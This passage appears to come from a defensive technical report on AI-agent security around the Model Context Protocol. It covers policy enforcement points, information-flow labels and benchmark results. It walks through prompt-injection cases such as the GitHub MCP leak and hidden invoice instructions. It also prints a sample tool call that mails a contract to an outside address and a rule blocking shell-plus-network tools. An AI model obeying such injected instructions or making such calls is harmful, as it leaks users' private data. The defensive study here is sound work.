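Anbiaee and colleagues compared MCP with three protocols that mainly connect agents to each other. Google's Agent2Agent (A2A) lets one agent delegate a task to another. In Agora, agents negotiate a communication format by exchanging documents that describe it. The Agent Network Protocol (ANP) gives each agent a cryptographic identity so that agents from different organisations can find and verify each other.

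The researchers assessed twelve risks across creation, operation and update. Four of them show where the protocols differ:

| Risk | MCP | A2A | Agora | ANP |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Impersonation through a copied name | No rule that names must be unique | Agents declare their own identity | Agents name themselves | Cryptographic identifiers are unique |
| Unverified identity at registration | No strict check | Login tokens limit misuse | Proof is optional | Cryptographic proof |
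| Old credentials that survive an update | No forced withdrawal | Replacement possible but not required | Delegated roles can persist | Some credentials can persist |
| Unsigned updates | Signing not required | Verification optional | Forged documents can spread | Some dependencies can escape the check |

The first two risks depend on the protocol's design, since ANP largely avoids them. The last two affect all four protocols, so a company that switched from MCP to another would still have to manage updates and revoke credentials. Prompt injection is not among the twelve risks, but any protocol that delivers untrusted text to a model can expose the model to it.

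Anbiaee and colleagues rated each risk's likelihood and impact from 1 to 3 and multiplied the two. A product of 1 or 2 counts as low, 3 or 4 as medium, and 6 or 9 as high, so raising one rating from 2 to 3 can turn a medium risk into a high one. They say they based the ratings on the protocols' specifications and expert judgement because the protocols are too new to provide incident data. DREAD has the same weakness if the people scoring the risks have no data on attacks.

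At least one of the ratings is also based on a doubtful description of MCP, in which agents share their whole context with tools. MCP is designed to prevent servers from reading the whole conversation.

The researchers then tested one risk they consider specific to MCP. They connected a client to a legitimate payment server and an attacker's server that both offered a tool with the same name, and counted how often the client called the wrong one.

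| How the client chooses | Condition | Wrong server in 100 trials |
|---|---|---|
| First match | Honest server listed first | 0 |
| First match | Attacker's server listed first | 100 |
| Best description | Honest tool has the more convincing description | 0 |
| Best description | Attacker's tool has the more convincing description | 100 |
| Best description, random choice if tied | Identical descriptions | 52 |

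These results follow almost directly from the rules the researchers gave the client. A client that takes the first match will always call the attacker's tool if that tool is listed first, and a random choice between two tools will be wrong about half the time. The experiment shows that a shared name is dangerous if the client has no other way to tell tools apart. Separate namespaces would prevent this mistake, and the experiment doesn't show how often real hosts make it.

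### The OWASP lists

OWASP publishes short lists for practitioners. Besides the MCP list mentioned in the section on login, it has a *Top 10 for Agentic Applications* for 2026, which covers agents in general. The examples below come from *MCP-38*, which matched its own threats to that list.

| Code | OWASP category | Matching MCP threat |
|---|---|---|
| ASI01 | Agent goal hijack | Instructions hidden in a fetched document |
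| ASI02 | Tool misuse and exploitation | Harmless tools combined to steal data |
| ASI03 | Identity and privilege abuse | A stolen access token |
| ASI04 | Agentic supply chain vulnerabilities | A malicious package or a rug pull |
| ASI05 | Unexpected code execution | Command injection |
| ASI06 | Memory and context poisoning | Instructions in a parameter's description |
| ASI07 | Insecure inter-agent communication | A replayed message |
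| ASI08 | Cascading failures | Tool calls that exhaust a budget or server |
| ASI09 | Human-agent trust exploitation | Approval requests that wear the user down |
| ASI10 | Rogue agents | An agent that gradually drifts from its task |

Categories this broad are hard to apply consistently. For example, *MCP-38* assigns an attacker's instruction to ASI04 if it is in a tool's main description and to ASI06 if it is in a parameter's description, although the host can check both fields in the same way. A company that divided work among its teams by OWASP category could end up with two teams responsible for one check.

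### The NSA's information sheet

NSA's *Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2026) is an information sheet that the US National Security Agency published in May 2026. For advice on agents in general, it refers readers to *Careful Adoption of Agentic AI Services*, joint guidance from April 2026 that it credits to the Australian Signals Directorate's cyber security centre. The sheet itself deals with the protocol and how people use it. It raises eight concerns:

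| Concern | The NSA's criticism |
|---|---|
| Access control | Developers may leave out authorization, and servers and clients can't exchange role-based permissions when they connect |
| Data formats | Messages can contain code or instructions, and each developer decides how strictly to check them |
| Approval | A server that a user has approved can often gain new abilities without a new request |
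| Tokens and sessions | The protocol doesn't require rules for renewing or withdrawing tokens, and attackers may hijack sessions |
| Misconfiguration | Developers may later use a simple, unprotected server for sensitive data |
| Inconsistent behaviour | Different agents can interpret the same request differently, which an attacker may exploit |
| Audit logs | Many implementations record little or nothing |
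| Denial of service | Complex or repeating tasks can exhaust a server |

The sheet supports these concerns with six examples that it describes as identified or exploited in the real world, but the strength of the evidence varies widely. The WhatsApp case is a demonstration by Invariant Labs, and the MCP Inspector flaw is a reported vulnerability. In another case, the server for GitHub, a site where developers store code, had such broad access that an agent could copy data from private projects into public ones. *MCP-38* presents this as an attack confirmed in production, but the NSA's source is again a publication by Invariant Labs, so it may also have been a demonstration.

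The NSA makes nine recommendations:

1. Choose projects that someone still maintains, and review their code.
2. Separate tools for public data from tools for sensitive data, and filter outgoing connections.
3. Check every argument against its schema, its expected range and the setting in which the tool will use it.
4. Run tools in a sandbox with few permissions.
5. Sign messages, and give them an expiry time so that an attacker can't reuse them.
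6. Treat the output of every tool as untrusted input to the next step.
7. Log each call with its exact parameters and the identities involved.
8. Keep an inventory of servers and fix known flaws.
9. Scan the organisation's network for MCP servers that nobody has approved.

Most of these are established security practices that a company can adopt without waiting for a new version of the protocol. Signing messages is harder because the client and server must support the same extension. The NSA prefers local servers for private data. They keep the data away from outside operators, but they normally run with the user's permissions, so this advice depends on also following the fourth recommendation.

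### What the July 2026 specification changed

The NSA criticized the November 2025 specification of MCP. One of its main objections was that the protocol let servers send requests to clients, which reverses the usual relationship between the two. The July 2026 version largely resolves this because servers can no longer send such requests.

Removing protocol-level sessions partly resolves the concern about hijacking, but servers that accept older clients or don't check handles still carry a similar risk. The new login rules don't set a maximum lifetime for tokens.

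Gateways can now log tool names more easily because they can read them from the request header. The header doesn't include the arguments or the reason for the call, and the protocol's own logging feature is being phased out. Developers still have to decide what to record and how long to keep it.

The criticisms of access control and approval both still apply. Authorization is still optional, and a server may still change its tools after the employee approves them. The host asks the employee again only if its developer has added that check.

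## Checking each tool call against a policy

The software that runs the office assistant's tool calls can first check each one against a policy, a machine-readable rule that states which actions are allowed in which circumstances. The point where the software holds a call for this check is called the enforcement point.

### What an enforcement point must guarantee

Computer security researchers set out three requirements for such a component in the 1970s and called it a reference monitor.

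A policy check needs to cover every action an agent takes, because an attacker needs only one unchecked route to a mail server. In *AEGIS*, Yuan, Su and Zhao (2026) describe a system that intercepts an agent's tool calls inside the software libraries the agent uses. They state that the system doesn't protect against calls made outside those libraries, so a script that the agent writes and runs could bypass it.

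**The agent must not be able to alter the monitor or its policy.** The Windsurf editor changed its own configuration after reading hidden instructions, and an agent could likewise change a policy file stored in a folder it can write to. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (Palumbo, Choudhary et al., 2026) therefore excludes from its guarantee any policy that lets the agent modify the policy or the monitor's process.

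The mechanism that checks tool calls should be small enough for people to review and test all of it. A short program that compares a call's arguments with a list of rules can meet this requirement, but a sentence in the model's context such as "never send contracts outside the company" doesn't, because nobody can verify how a large model will weigh it against an injected instruction.

### Where to put the check

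Developers can place the check in the agent's own code, in a gateway between the client and the servers, or in the operating system.

| Position | What it can check | What it misses |
|---|---|---|
| Hook in the agent's code | Every call the hooked function handles, including built-in tools, along with the user's request | Actions by code that doesn't use that function |
| Gateway | The name, arguments and result of each call sent through it | Built-in tools, most of the conversation and the effects of a shell command |
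| Operating system | The files, connections and programs that a local process opens | The purpose of an action, and anything on another company's machines |

**A hook** has the most information about the task. *AgentSpec* (Wang, Poskitt and Sun, 2025) hooks into LangChain, a framework for building agents, to run its checks just before an action. But a hook usually runs in the same process as the agent, so an injected instruction may be able to remove it if the agent can run code there.

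**A gateway** can run on a machine the agent can't access, and it can apply one policy to agents from several vendors. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) offers its policy system as both a library and a proxy. To use the proxy, a user only has to change the addresses the agent uses to reach its model and MCP servers. However, tools built into the agent bypass the proxy. The assistant's file server would too, unless the employer reroutes it, because the host starts that server as a local subprocess.

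A gateway also can't check what a command does after it starts. If the employee adds a tool that runs shell commands, the gateway may receive the text `python cleanup.py`, which doesn't show what files the script will delete.

**The operating system** can block those deletions one by one, as in the sandbox described earlier, but it has little information about their purpose. Ravindran and Deochake (2026) point out in *ToolGuardian* that a network connection in a trace of system calls may be normal use of a service or a theft of data. The employer's mail server receives an encrypted connection in both cases. A company that wants to control both email recipients and shell commands therefore needs checks in more than one place.

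### What the 2026 headers give a gateway

A gateway can use the `Mcp-Method` and `Mcp-Name` headers to block a tool by name, limit how often an agent calls it, or send calls to risky tools through a slower check. Without protocol-level sessions, any copy of the gateway can handle any request, but rules that depend on earlier calls still require a record that all copies share.

To enforce a rule about an email's recipient, the gateway still has to read the request body, which contains the arguments. A gateway that reads the body should also check that it matches the headers instead of relying on every server to reject a mismatch. Older clients don't send the headers, so the gateway has to read the body of each of their requests or refuse the request.

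The gateway could also remove forbidden tools from the list a server returns, so that the model never reads their definitions. The Model Context Protocol now lets these lists specify how long clients may store them and whether users may share a copy. A gateway that gives employees different lists has to forbid sharing. The gateway must still check each call, because a client may have an older list.

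### One mail call from start to finish

Suppose the instruction hidden in the supplier's invoice works, and the model requests this call:

```json
{
  "name": "send_mail",
  "arguments": {
    "to": "archive@outside.example",
    "subject": "Contract",
    "body": "The contract is attached.",
    "attachments": ["contracts/supplier.pdf"]
  }
}
```

The employer has the following policy, written here in a notation close to Progent's. The word `match` compares a value with a text pattern.

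```
forbid send_mail when { not (attachments.length == 0) and
                        not (to match "^[a-z.]+@employer\.example$") }
allow  send_mail when { to match "^[a-z.]+@employer\.example$" }
allow  send_mail when { to == "billing@supplier.example" }
allow  read_mail
allow  search_files
allow  read_file when { path match "^contracts/[a-z0-9-]+\.pdf$" }
allow  convert_currency when { to == "USD" }
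```

The enforcement point handles the call in five steps:

1. **Parse.** It reads the tool's name and arguments and rejects a call that doesn't fit the tool's schema. It has to interpret the address exactly as the mail server will, or an attacker could write one that passes the check and leads elsewhere.
2. **Gather context.** It looks up other facts the rules may need, such as whose access token the call uses or which data labels apply.
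3. **Evaluate.** It tests the `forbid` rules before the `allow` rules. This call has an attachment and an outside recipient, so the `forbid` rule applies.
4. **Act.** It can allow the call, deny it, rewrite it or ask a person. Here it denies the call and returns an error with the reason, so that the model can continue with the invoice.
5. **Record.** It stores the call, the rule that applied, the version of the policy and the outcome.

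The facts in step 2 have to come from a source the model can't invent. *NOMOS* (Yu, Kim and Choi, 2026) takes them only from the user's messages and from fields in actual tool results. If an injected instruction makes the model claim that the employee has approved a message, the claim has no effect.

When the enforcement point rewrites a tool call, the result returned to the model should describe the change. Otherwise, if the enforcement point removed the attachment and sent the rest, the model might tell the employee that it had sent the contract.

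The same policy gives these outcomes for other calls:

| Proposed call | Rule that applies | Outcome |
|---|---|---|
| The contract's text, without an attachment, to `archive@outside.example` | None | Denied |
| A question to `billing@supplier.example` | `allow` for the supplier | Allowed |
| A call to `delete_mail`, a tool the server added yesterday | None | Denied |
| False bank details to `finance@employer.example` | `allow` for colleagues | Allowed |

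Default denial blocks any call that no rule allows, including those in the first and third rows, so nobody had to foresee the new tool. If calls were allowed by default, the employer would need a `forbid` rule for every harmful call an attacker might think of.

The policy permits the attack in the last row, which is one of those the employer most wants to prevent. The check also ends when the call reaches the server, so it can't detect changes the server makes afterwards, such as the hidden recipient that postmark-mcp added to each email.

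### Progent

Progent uses rules that allow or forbid a tool call depending on its arguments, and it blocks calls that match no rule. A rule can also specify whether Progent responds to a blocked call by stopping the agent, notifying the user or returning an error message to the model.

A policy that suits every task is usually too broad, so Progent has a language model write one for each user request. This model initially reads only the request and the list of tools, which the developers assume no attacker controls. As the agent works, the model can propose changes to the policy, such as adding a tool that the task turns out to need or limiting messages to a recipient whose name the agent has just looked up.

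Such a change is dangerous after the agent has read a malicious invoice. Progent therefore compares the old policy *P* with the proposed policy *P′*. If *A(P)* is the set of all calls that *P* allows, the change is safe to apply when

*A(P′) ⊆ A(P)*,

which means that the new policy allows nothing the old one blocked. An SMT solver, a program that checks whether logical conditions can hold together, searches for a call that *P′* allows and *P* blocks. If there is none, Progent applies the change. Otherwise, the change is an expansion and needs approval. Between approvals, the set of allowed calls can only stay the same or shrink, even if the invoice fools the model that writes the policy.

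*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) warns that Progent's updates may loosen the limits when a tool result contains malicious text. The solver now prevents this from happening silently, but a person may still approve the wrong change.

Shi and colleagues tested Progent on two collections of prompt injection tests, AgentDojo and Agent Security Bench (ASB). AgentDojo combines ordinary tasks in banking, messaging, travel and office work with instructions that an attacker has hidden in the data. With GPT-4o as both the agent and the policy writer, Progent lowered the attack success rate on AgentDojo from 39.9% to 1.0%. On ASB, the rate fell from 70.3% to 3.9% with Progent. Many of the remaining failures on ASB involved malicious tools whose names and descriptions resembled those of genuine ones.

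The researchers approved every expansion automatically in these tests, to imitate a careless user. The 1.0% therefore measures how well GPT-4o wrote policies without the approval step. The initial policies, without updates, reduced the rate to 2.5%. When people reviewed the initial policy and each expansion, the rate was 0%. Only 6% of proposed updates were expansions, so reviewers had few decisions to make.

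Progent also helped models that already resisted most attacks. The attack success rate for Claude Sonnet 4 fell from 6.8% to 0.5%. Task success stayed close to the unprotected agent's. Yu and colleagues report that an earlier version of the Progent paper gave task success rates of 76.3% with Progent and 79.4% without a defence.

These results exclude two AgentDojo attacks that steer the agent towards a different but legitimate hotel. Progent can't block an action that the task permits, and it doesn't check the agent's written answers.

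### AgentSpec and Cedar

An AgentSpec rule names an event, the conditions to check and the response. Adapted from the paper's example about bank transfers, a rule for the mail server could look like this:

```
rule @inspect_outside_mail
trigger send_mail
check
    !is_to_colleague
enforce
    user_inspection
end
```

The exclamation mark means "not", so the agent has to ask the user before it writes to an outsider. A developer has to supply the code behind `is_to_colleague`. A rule can also stop the agent, run a different action, or have the model reconsider. AgentSpec allows any action to which no rule applies.

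Wang and colleagues tested AgentSpec on agents that run program code, control household robots or drive cars. It stopped more than 90% of the unsafe code executions, all the hazardous robot actions and every traffic violation in the driving scenarios. The checks added milliseconds of delay. These tests covered dangerous actions in general, so they don't show how well AgentSpec would stop an attacker who hides instructions in an invoice.

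Rules written by OpenAI's o1 model did less well. For the robots, 95.56% of the actions these rules flagged were hazardous, but the rules caught only 70.96% of all hazards. They prevented violations in five of the eight driving scenarios.

Cedar is an open-source policy language from Amazon Web Services that developers also use for ordinary applications. In a Cedar-based gateway, each tool call becomes a question about who wants to do what to which resource, and the arguments serve as context:

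```
permit (
  principal in Group::"Purchasing",
  action == Action::"send_mail",
  resource == Server::"mail"
) when { context.to like "*@employer.example" };
```

Cedar denies a request by default, and a `forbid` rule overrides any `permit` rule. The language is deliberately limited, so a separate analyser can check a whole set of policies for conflicting rules and rules that never apply before anyone uses it. Yu and colleagues report that Mondl and colleagues used the analyser to correct Cedar policies that a language model had written from an agent's instructions, then replayed recorded runs to measure how much of the instructions the policies covered. The replay did not measure how many attacks a working gateway would stop.

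### The March 2026 interception layer

AEGIS combines a hook with a separate decision service. Its library patches 14 agent frameworks, so developers don't have to rewrite their agents. When the model requests a tool, the library pauses the agent and sends the call to the service, which works in three stages:

1. It extracts every piece of text from the arguments, down to 32 levels of nesting. If an argument is too deep or too large to search completely, it marks the call as suspicious.
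2. It compares the text with 22 patterns for known dangers, such as malicious database commands and paths to password files.
3. It checks the call against the operator's policies and then allows it, blocks it or holds it for a person.

Yuan and colleagues report that AEGIS blocked all 48 attacks in their test. They selected the attacks from published techniques, so the result doesn't show how well its patterns would perform against new attacks. Of 500 harmless calls, AEGIS stopped six (1.2%). All six were database queries that contained an "or" condition, which attackers also use.

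The median delay over 1,000 calls was 8.3 milliseconds, and 99% of calls took no more than 23.1 milliseconds, though a graph in the paper gives slightly different values. Users would hardly notice this delay, since a model typically needs between one and thirty seconds to respond. However, the measured service ran on the same machine or network as the agent, and a distant gateway would take longer.

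The patterns are useful against arguments that are dangerous in themselves, such as a database command that deletes a table. An email to an outside address contains no such argument, so the operator still has to write a rule about recipients.

### Turning written policies into rules

People can write rules by hand if the policy is short. Yu and colleagues cite an experiment with an airline service agent in which four hand-written checks raised GPT-4o-mini's task success from 29.6% to 42.0%. But someone has to maintain these rules, and most companies keep their policies in documents written for employees.

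NOMOS, from the company Corners, converts such a document into rules before the agent starts work:

1. A program divides the document into clauses.
2. A language model proposes rules for each clause. It does this five times, because its answers vary.
3. A program checks whether each proposed rule can work with the available tools, and repairs or rejects those that can't.
4. The rules that appear in most of the five attempts go into the final set, each with the clause it came from.

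A rule either forbids a call while a condition holds or blocks it until a condition holds. The model has to choose the condition from a fixed list that a person prepared for that kind of business. While the agent works, a simple program applies the rules without calling a model.

The checks in step 3 are necessary because many of the proposed rules would not have worked. The model turned the clause "authenticate the user at the beginning of the conversation" into a rule that blocked every tool until the user had logged in, including the two tools needed to log in. Another rule would have required the customer's approval just to look up a flight. Structural defects of this kind affected 29 of the 79 rules proposed for the airline policy and 7 of the 53 proposed for the retail policy. After the program also merged duplicates, 10 airline rules and 5 retail rules remained.

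The researchers then switched the checks off and processed a separate set of proposals. Eight of the 14 resulting airline rules and three of the five retail rules couldn't function.

### Results on τ²-bench

τ-bench and its successor, τ²-bench, test customer service agents that have to follow a company's written policy. A second model plays the customer, and the agent can use tools to change bookings or orders. The benchmark mainly scores the final state of the database. Agents often succeed once and fail when they repeat a task, so the benchmark reports pass^k, the estimated probability that an agent completes the same task in all of *k* attempts. With *c* successes in *n* trials, the estimate is

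pass^k = C(c, k) / C(n, k),

where C(a, b) is the number of ways to choose *b* items from *a*. An agent that succeeds in three of five trials has a pass^1 of 60%. Its pass^2 is only 30%, because three of the ten possible pairs of trials consist of two successes.

Yu and colleagues tested NOMOS with an agent based on the 26-billion-parameter Gemma 4. They counted violations with a separate set of hand-written rules:

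| Domain | Changes that violated the policy, without and with NOMOS | pass^1, without and with NOMOS |
|---|---|---|
| Airline | 66.3% and 2.6% | 39.2% and 47.6% |
| Retail | 30.8% and 6.9% | 52.4% and 50.2% |

The violation rates depend on how strictly one reads the policy. If a customer's single "yes" can approve several announced changes, the rates without NOMOS fall to 36.8% and 13.6%, and the rates with it are 2.6% and 5.3%. Neither change in pass^1 is statistically significant, but the airline agent's improvements in pass^2 to pass^4 are. In the airline tests, an agent that breaks the policy often leaves the database in the wrong state, so preventing the violation can also help the agent complete the task.

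NOMOS also reduced the number of changes the airline agent made, from 353 to 116. The retail agent made almost as many changes as before (582, compared with 611), so inactivity can't explain the improvement there.

Each decision took three microseconds on average. This time covers only evaluating the rules, whereas the figure for AEGIS includes sending the call to another program and back.

### Results on AgentDojo

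AgentDojo has no written policies, so the researchers wrote a one-page policy for each of its four areas. They already knew the attacks when they wrote these policies, so the results are less independent than those on τ²-bench.

| Area | Attack success rate, without and with NOMOS | Task success when there was no attack |
|---|---|---|
| Banking | 46.5% and 0.0% | 79.2% and 70.8% |
| Slack (workplace messaging) | 70.5% and 0.0% | 90.5% and 14.3% |
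| Travel | 10.0% and 3.6% | 75.0% and 70.0% |
| Workspace (mail, calendar and files) | 7.3% and 0.0% | 87.5% and 65.0% |

NOMOS made the agent nearly useless on the messaging tasks. Its rules block the agent from sending anything to a person, channel or web address that the user hasn't named. Many legitimate tasks require the agent to find the recipient in an earlier message, which is also where an attacker would put an address.

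The banking figure of 0.0% also leaves out some unwanted payments. In 8 of the 288 attack runs, the injected instruction led the agent to pay someone the user had paid before, which the policy allows.

The researchers also ran Progent on the banking tasks with the same Gemma model. Progent reduced the attack success rate from 46.5% to 5.6%, and task success without an attack fell to 62.5%. The comparison comes from developers of a competing system, and with only 16 tasks, the difference in task success between the two systems could be due to chance.

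A policy derived from the user's request can't specify details that the request omits. Of the 16 attacks that still succeeded against Progent, 12 occurred in two tasks where the user asked the agent to pay a bill without naming the account, so the policy allowed payment to the attacker's account. NOMOS blocked these payments because the company's policy limits payments to known recipients. In one of the two tasks, the same rule also blocked the legitimate payment.

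### Logic rules, heuristics or a model

Ravindran and Deochake compared three ways to evaluate a policy, all with the same facts about each tool and task. One used logic rules, such as this rule against tools that can both run shell commands and reach the network:

```
deny(Tool) :-
    capability(Tool, shell_exec),
    network_access(Tool).
```

The second evaluator was a conventional program with risk scores and thresholds. The third was a language model that received the facts and written policy instructions.

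The researchers tested whether each of three evaluators would permit the right actions in 20 scenarios. Some scenarios had a single call, and others had several calls that were dangerous only in combination. All three evaluators decided every scenario correctly, so the test was too easy to rank them. Performance fell substantially when the researchers removed the policy's rules about combinations of tools and about differences between what a tool was supposed to do and what it did, so on this small test the content of the policy mattered more than the type of evaluator.

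ToolGuardian also vetted 16 tools before use, half of them malicious. The logic rules were 88% accurate when given each tool's description, a trace of its system calls and its observed effects. The reported scores are consistent with the rules rejecting six of the eight malicious tools and none of the harmless ones. Adding source code analysis revealed more dangerous behaviour but also led to more rejections of harmless tools with broad abilities.

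The NOMOS paper provides better evidence on how using a model affects speed and reliability. It compares fixed rules with a rebuilt version of a system in which a language model reads the conversation and judges each change the airline agent tries to make. Task success was about the same, but the average run took 37.1 seconds with the model and 21.3 with the rules. With a judging model that ran locally, pass^5 fell to 16.0%, half the rate with fixed rules. Logic rules also give the same answer every time and identify the rule responsible, which helps when an employee asks why the assistant refused a request.

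### When the policy is wrong

An enforcement point can work perfectly and still apply a bad policy. Palumbo and colleagues state this limit openly, since their guarantee assumes that the policy expresses what the user intends. The NOMOS tests contain several examples:

- **Too strict.** The airline's policy forbids changes to the flights of a basic economy booking but permits an upgrade to a better cabin. The compiled rule blocked both because both use the same tool.
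- **Too weak.** The travel policy permits only calendar events that the user has requested. The compiled rule checked whether the user had requested any change at all, so an attacker's event got through when the user had asked for an email.
- **Incomplete.** The compiled retail rules had nothing on two clauses about refunds and exchanges. Those clauses account for 21 of the 40 violations that remained.

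Developers have several ways to look for such mistakes before an agent goes into use, and each can miss some of them.

**Structural checks** find rules that can never work (NOMOS) or that conflict with each other (Cedar's analyser). They don't check whether a rule matches the meaning of its clause. NOMOS checks for deadlocks one rule at a time, so it can pass two rules that each block the tool needed to satisfy the other.

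**Replaying recorded runs** shows how often a rule would have blocked an agent that was doing its job. A NOMOS rule for a telephone company would have refused 47 of 49 payment requests in successful runs, because the model had reversed the meaning of the clause. The replay flagged this rule, but NOMOS flags a rule only if it would refuse at least 90% of a tool's calls in successful runs. None of the airline rules reached that level, so the replay didn't flag the overly strict cabin rule. A replay also can't show what the agent would have done after a refusal.

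**Example tests and proofs** check a rule against a separate statement of what it should do. Yu and colleagues describe a system that generates compliant and non-compliant calls, then rewrites its rules until they handle all of them correctly. VeriGuard proves that its policy code satisfies a formal specification. Either check is only as reliable as its examples or specification, which may contain the same misunderstanding as the rule.

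This happened in the NOMOS evaluation. The researchers' hand-written rules for counting violations also treated a cabin upgrade as a forbidden flight change, so comparing the two sets of rules couldn't reveal the mistake. The researchers found it when they had another model, Claude Sonnet 4.5, review the refused calls and then checked its objections against the policy and the records. But in an earlier audit, Claude had disagreed with the hand-written rules in 77 cases, and in 30 of them it had facts in the transcript wrong.

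For the office assistant, the employer could replay a month of ordinary work against the mail policy and then try known attacks. The replay would probably show that employees often write to the finance department, so the employer would keep the rule that allows it. That rule would also allow the message with false bank details, which uses the same tool and recipient as legitimate messages. To stop it, the enforcement point would have to detect that the account number came from the supplier's invoice, which it can't do from the call's arguments alone.

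## Tracking data as it moves between tools

Knowing where data came from would help the host stop both the message with the false bank details and leaks in which every call looks harmless. The employee's job involves reading invoices, opening contracts and sending mail, so a policy that examines one call at a time may allow each of these actions. An attacker who combines them can obtain the contract.

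### How harmless tools combine to leak data

Willison, the programmer who coined the term "prompt injection", warns against giving an agent three things at once: access to private data, exposure to text that an attacker may have written, and a way to send data out (*The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, 2025).

The mail server alone gives the office assistant all three. The inbox contains private messages, anyone can send mail to it, and `send_mail` can reach any address. Removing `send_mail` might not prevent leaks, because an agent can also put data in the web address of an image it loads or a link it shows the user to click.

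Willison argues that MCP makes this combination likely because it encourages users to mix tools from different sources. When researchers reported such leaks in finished products, the vendors usually closed the outgoing channel, but nobody does this for employees who combine tools themselves. Willison advises such users to avoid the combination entirely, but the office assistant would then have to stop either reading outside mail or sending messages.

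Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) demonstrates the problem with GitHub's official MCP server:

1. The attacker posts an issue, which is a public bug report, in the user's public code repository. It contains an instruction for AI agents.
2. The user asks Claude Desktop, running Claude 4 Opus, to look at the open issues.
3. The agent reads the issue, follows the instruction and reads the user's private repositories.
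4. The agent publishes what it found in a pull request, a proposed change to the code, in the public repository.

The pull request revealed the names of private repositories and the user's salary and plan to move to South America. Invariant Labs had prepared the repositories for a demonstration, so no real user's data was stolen. By default, Claude Desktop asks the user to confirm each call, but many users choose to always allow calls. GitHub can't solve the problem by patching the server, because the server worked as intended. Invariant Labs recommends a rule that limits an agent to one repository per session. That rule would have stopped this leak, but it would also block any legitimate task that involves two repositories.

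Willison's *21 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”* includes a similar case from later in 2025. PromptArmor hid an instruction in one-pixel type on a web page, and Google's Antigravity code editor collected credentials and code and sent them out through its browser.

In *Parasites in the Toolchain*, Zhao, Hou and colleagues (2025) measured how common tools that could be used in such attacks are. They call the three-phase attack MCP Unintended Privacy Disclosure (MCP-UPD). They collected 12,230 tools from 1,360 public servers and used a language model to pick out those an attacker might use. They then ran these tools in a real host and confirmed 1,062, or 8.7% of all the tools collected.

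| Phase | What the tool does | Confirmed tools | Servers with such a tool |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ingestion | Fetches outside text | 487 | 128 |
| Collection | Reads private data | 406 | 155 |
| Disclosure | Sends data out | 190 | 96 |

Only two tools could do all three, so most attackers would have to combine several. The counts may be too low because about 30% of the servers required accounts that the researchers could not easily get.

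Zhao and colleagues also built ten chains from popular tools and tested each one ten times in Cursor, set to run tool calls without asking. Nine chains leaked data at least once, but only 36 of the 100 trials did. The tenth combined a web scraper, a project planner and a music catalogue. The researchers think these tools had too little in common for the model to use them together.

Results varied widely by model. GPT-5 and Claude Sonnet 4.5 each resisted all 75 attempts, while Gemini 2.5 Flash leaked data in 53 of 75 and DeepSeek-R1 in 45 of 60. The developers of all four have since released newer models, and the researchers did not adapt their attacks to the models that resisted.

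A scanner that examines one tool at a time can't find these chains, a gap that *MCPThreatHive* reports in existing MCP security products.

### Labels for trust and confidentiality

Information-flow control attaches labels to data and checks them before the data leaves the system. The idea dates from the 1970s, and *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) applies it to agents, using two kinds of label. An integrity label marks data as trusted or untrusted, depending on whether an attacker could have influenced it. A confidentiality label can list the people who may read the data.

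When a program or model combines several inputs, the result gets the strictest label on each scale:

*trust(result) = the lowest trust among the inputs*

*readers(result) = readers(input 1) ∩ … ∩ readers(input n)*

The symbol ∩ means that only people on every list remain. If Ana, Ben and Carla may read one document and Ben, Carla and David may read another, only Ben and Carla may read a summary of both.

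The host then checks two conditions before a consequential call, meaning one with effects that matter, such as sending mail:

- **Trust.** The decision to make the call and all of its arguments must be trusted.
- **Confidentiality.** Every recipient must be among the permitted readers of the data in the call.

If the host checks only the confidentiality condition, it doesn't stop an injected instruction, but it limits who can receive the data. If the host checks only trust, users can still disclose secrets deliberately, because a call that no untrusted text has influenced is presumably what the user wanted.

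### The running example with labels

Suppose the supplier's invoice contains the hidden instruction to forward the contract. The employer has labelled outside mail as untrusted. The employee's copy of the contract contains internal notes, so only staff may read it.

| Step | Label of the new data | Label of the whole context afterwards |
|---|---|---|
| The employee's request | Trusted; anyone may read | Trusted; anyone may read |
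| Call 1: `read_mail` returns the invoice | Untrusted; staff and supplier | Untrusted; staff and supplier |
| Call 2: `read_file` returns the contract | Trusted; staff only | Untrusted; staff only |
| Call 3: `send_mail` to `archive@outside.example` | None, because the host blocks the call | Unchanged |

The model requests call 2 after reading the invoice, so an attacker may have influenced that request. The host still allows it because reading a local file sends no data out. Call 3 fails both conditions because the context is untrusted and the recipient isn't on staff. The host doesn't have to recognise the instruction as malicious, so the attacker gains nothing by rewording it.

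The trust condition also blocks the message with the false bank details. The finance department is allowed to read it, but the agent wrote it after reading untrusted text. For the same reason, the host would block a message giving the finance department the correct invoice total.

### When everything becomes untrusted

The context's label can only become stricter as the agent works. The host can't tell which part of the context led to which word of the output, because a language model processes its whole context together. Costa and colleagues' basic system therefore gives each response the combined label of everything the model has read. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) describes the result as label explosion, where every piece of data carries every label and the labels are no longer useful for making decisions.

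For the office assistant, this happens after one email. It can't send mail for the rest of the task, and it can't complete the conversion the employee asked for, because `convert_currency` would send the invoice total to an outside developer who isn't among the permitted readers.

Costa and colleagues describe one remedy, a system by Siddiqui and colleagues that works out which messages influenced a response, regenerates it from only those messages, and gives it their combined label. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* proposes replacing fixed labels with estimates of how much information an output carries about each source. CaMeL, FIDES, FORGE and ActGov instead change what the planning model reads or what the policy examines.

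### What AgentDojo measures

Researchers usually test these systems on AgentDojo, which Yu and colleagues also used to compare Progent and NOMOS. Each attack case pairs one user task with one attacker's goal. *ActGov* (Zhang, Peng and colleagues, 2026) reports 629 cases, while Palumbo and colleagues ran 949, presumably with a later version.

AgentDojo measures task success without an attack, task success during an attack, and attack success. These figures need to be read together, because a defence that blocks every call would have an attack success rate near zero but complete almost no tasks. AgentDojo also counts some attacks as successful if the agent attempts the harmful calls, even when a monitor blocks them.

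Zhang and colleagues also used AgentDyn, a newer benchmark with 60 user tasks and 560 attack cases. Its legitimate tasks often require the agent to take a recipient or another target from outside text, which also contains the attacker's instruction. This makes AgentDyn harder for defences that distrust all such text.

### CaMeL separates planning from reading

CaMeL, by Debenedetti and colleagues (2025), builds on Willison's dual-LLM pattern, which divides an agent's work between two models. According to *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025), a privileged model writes a plan from the user's request alone, and a quarantined model processes untrusted data but can't call tools. An interpreter carries out the plan, tracking where each value came from and checking a policy before every tool call.

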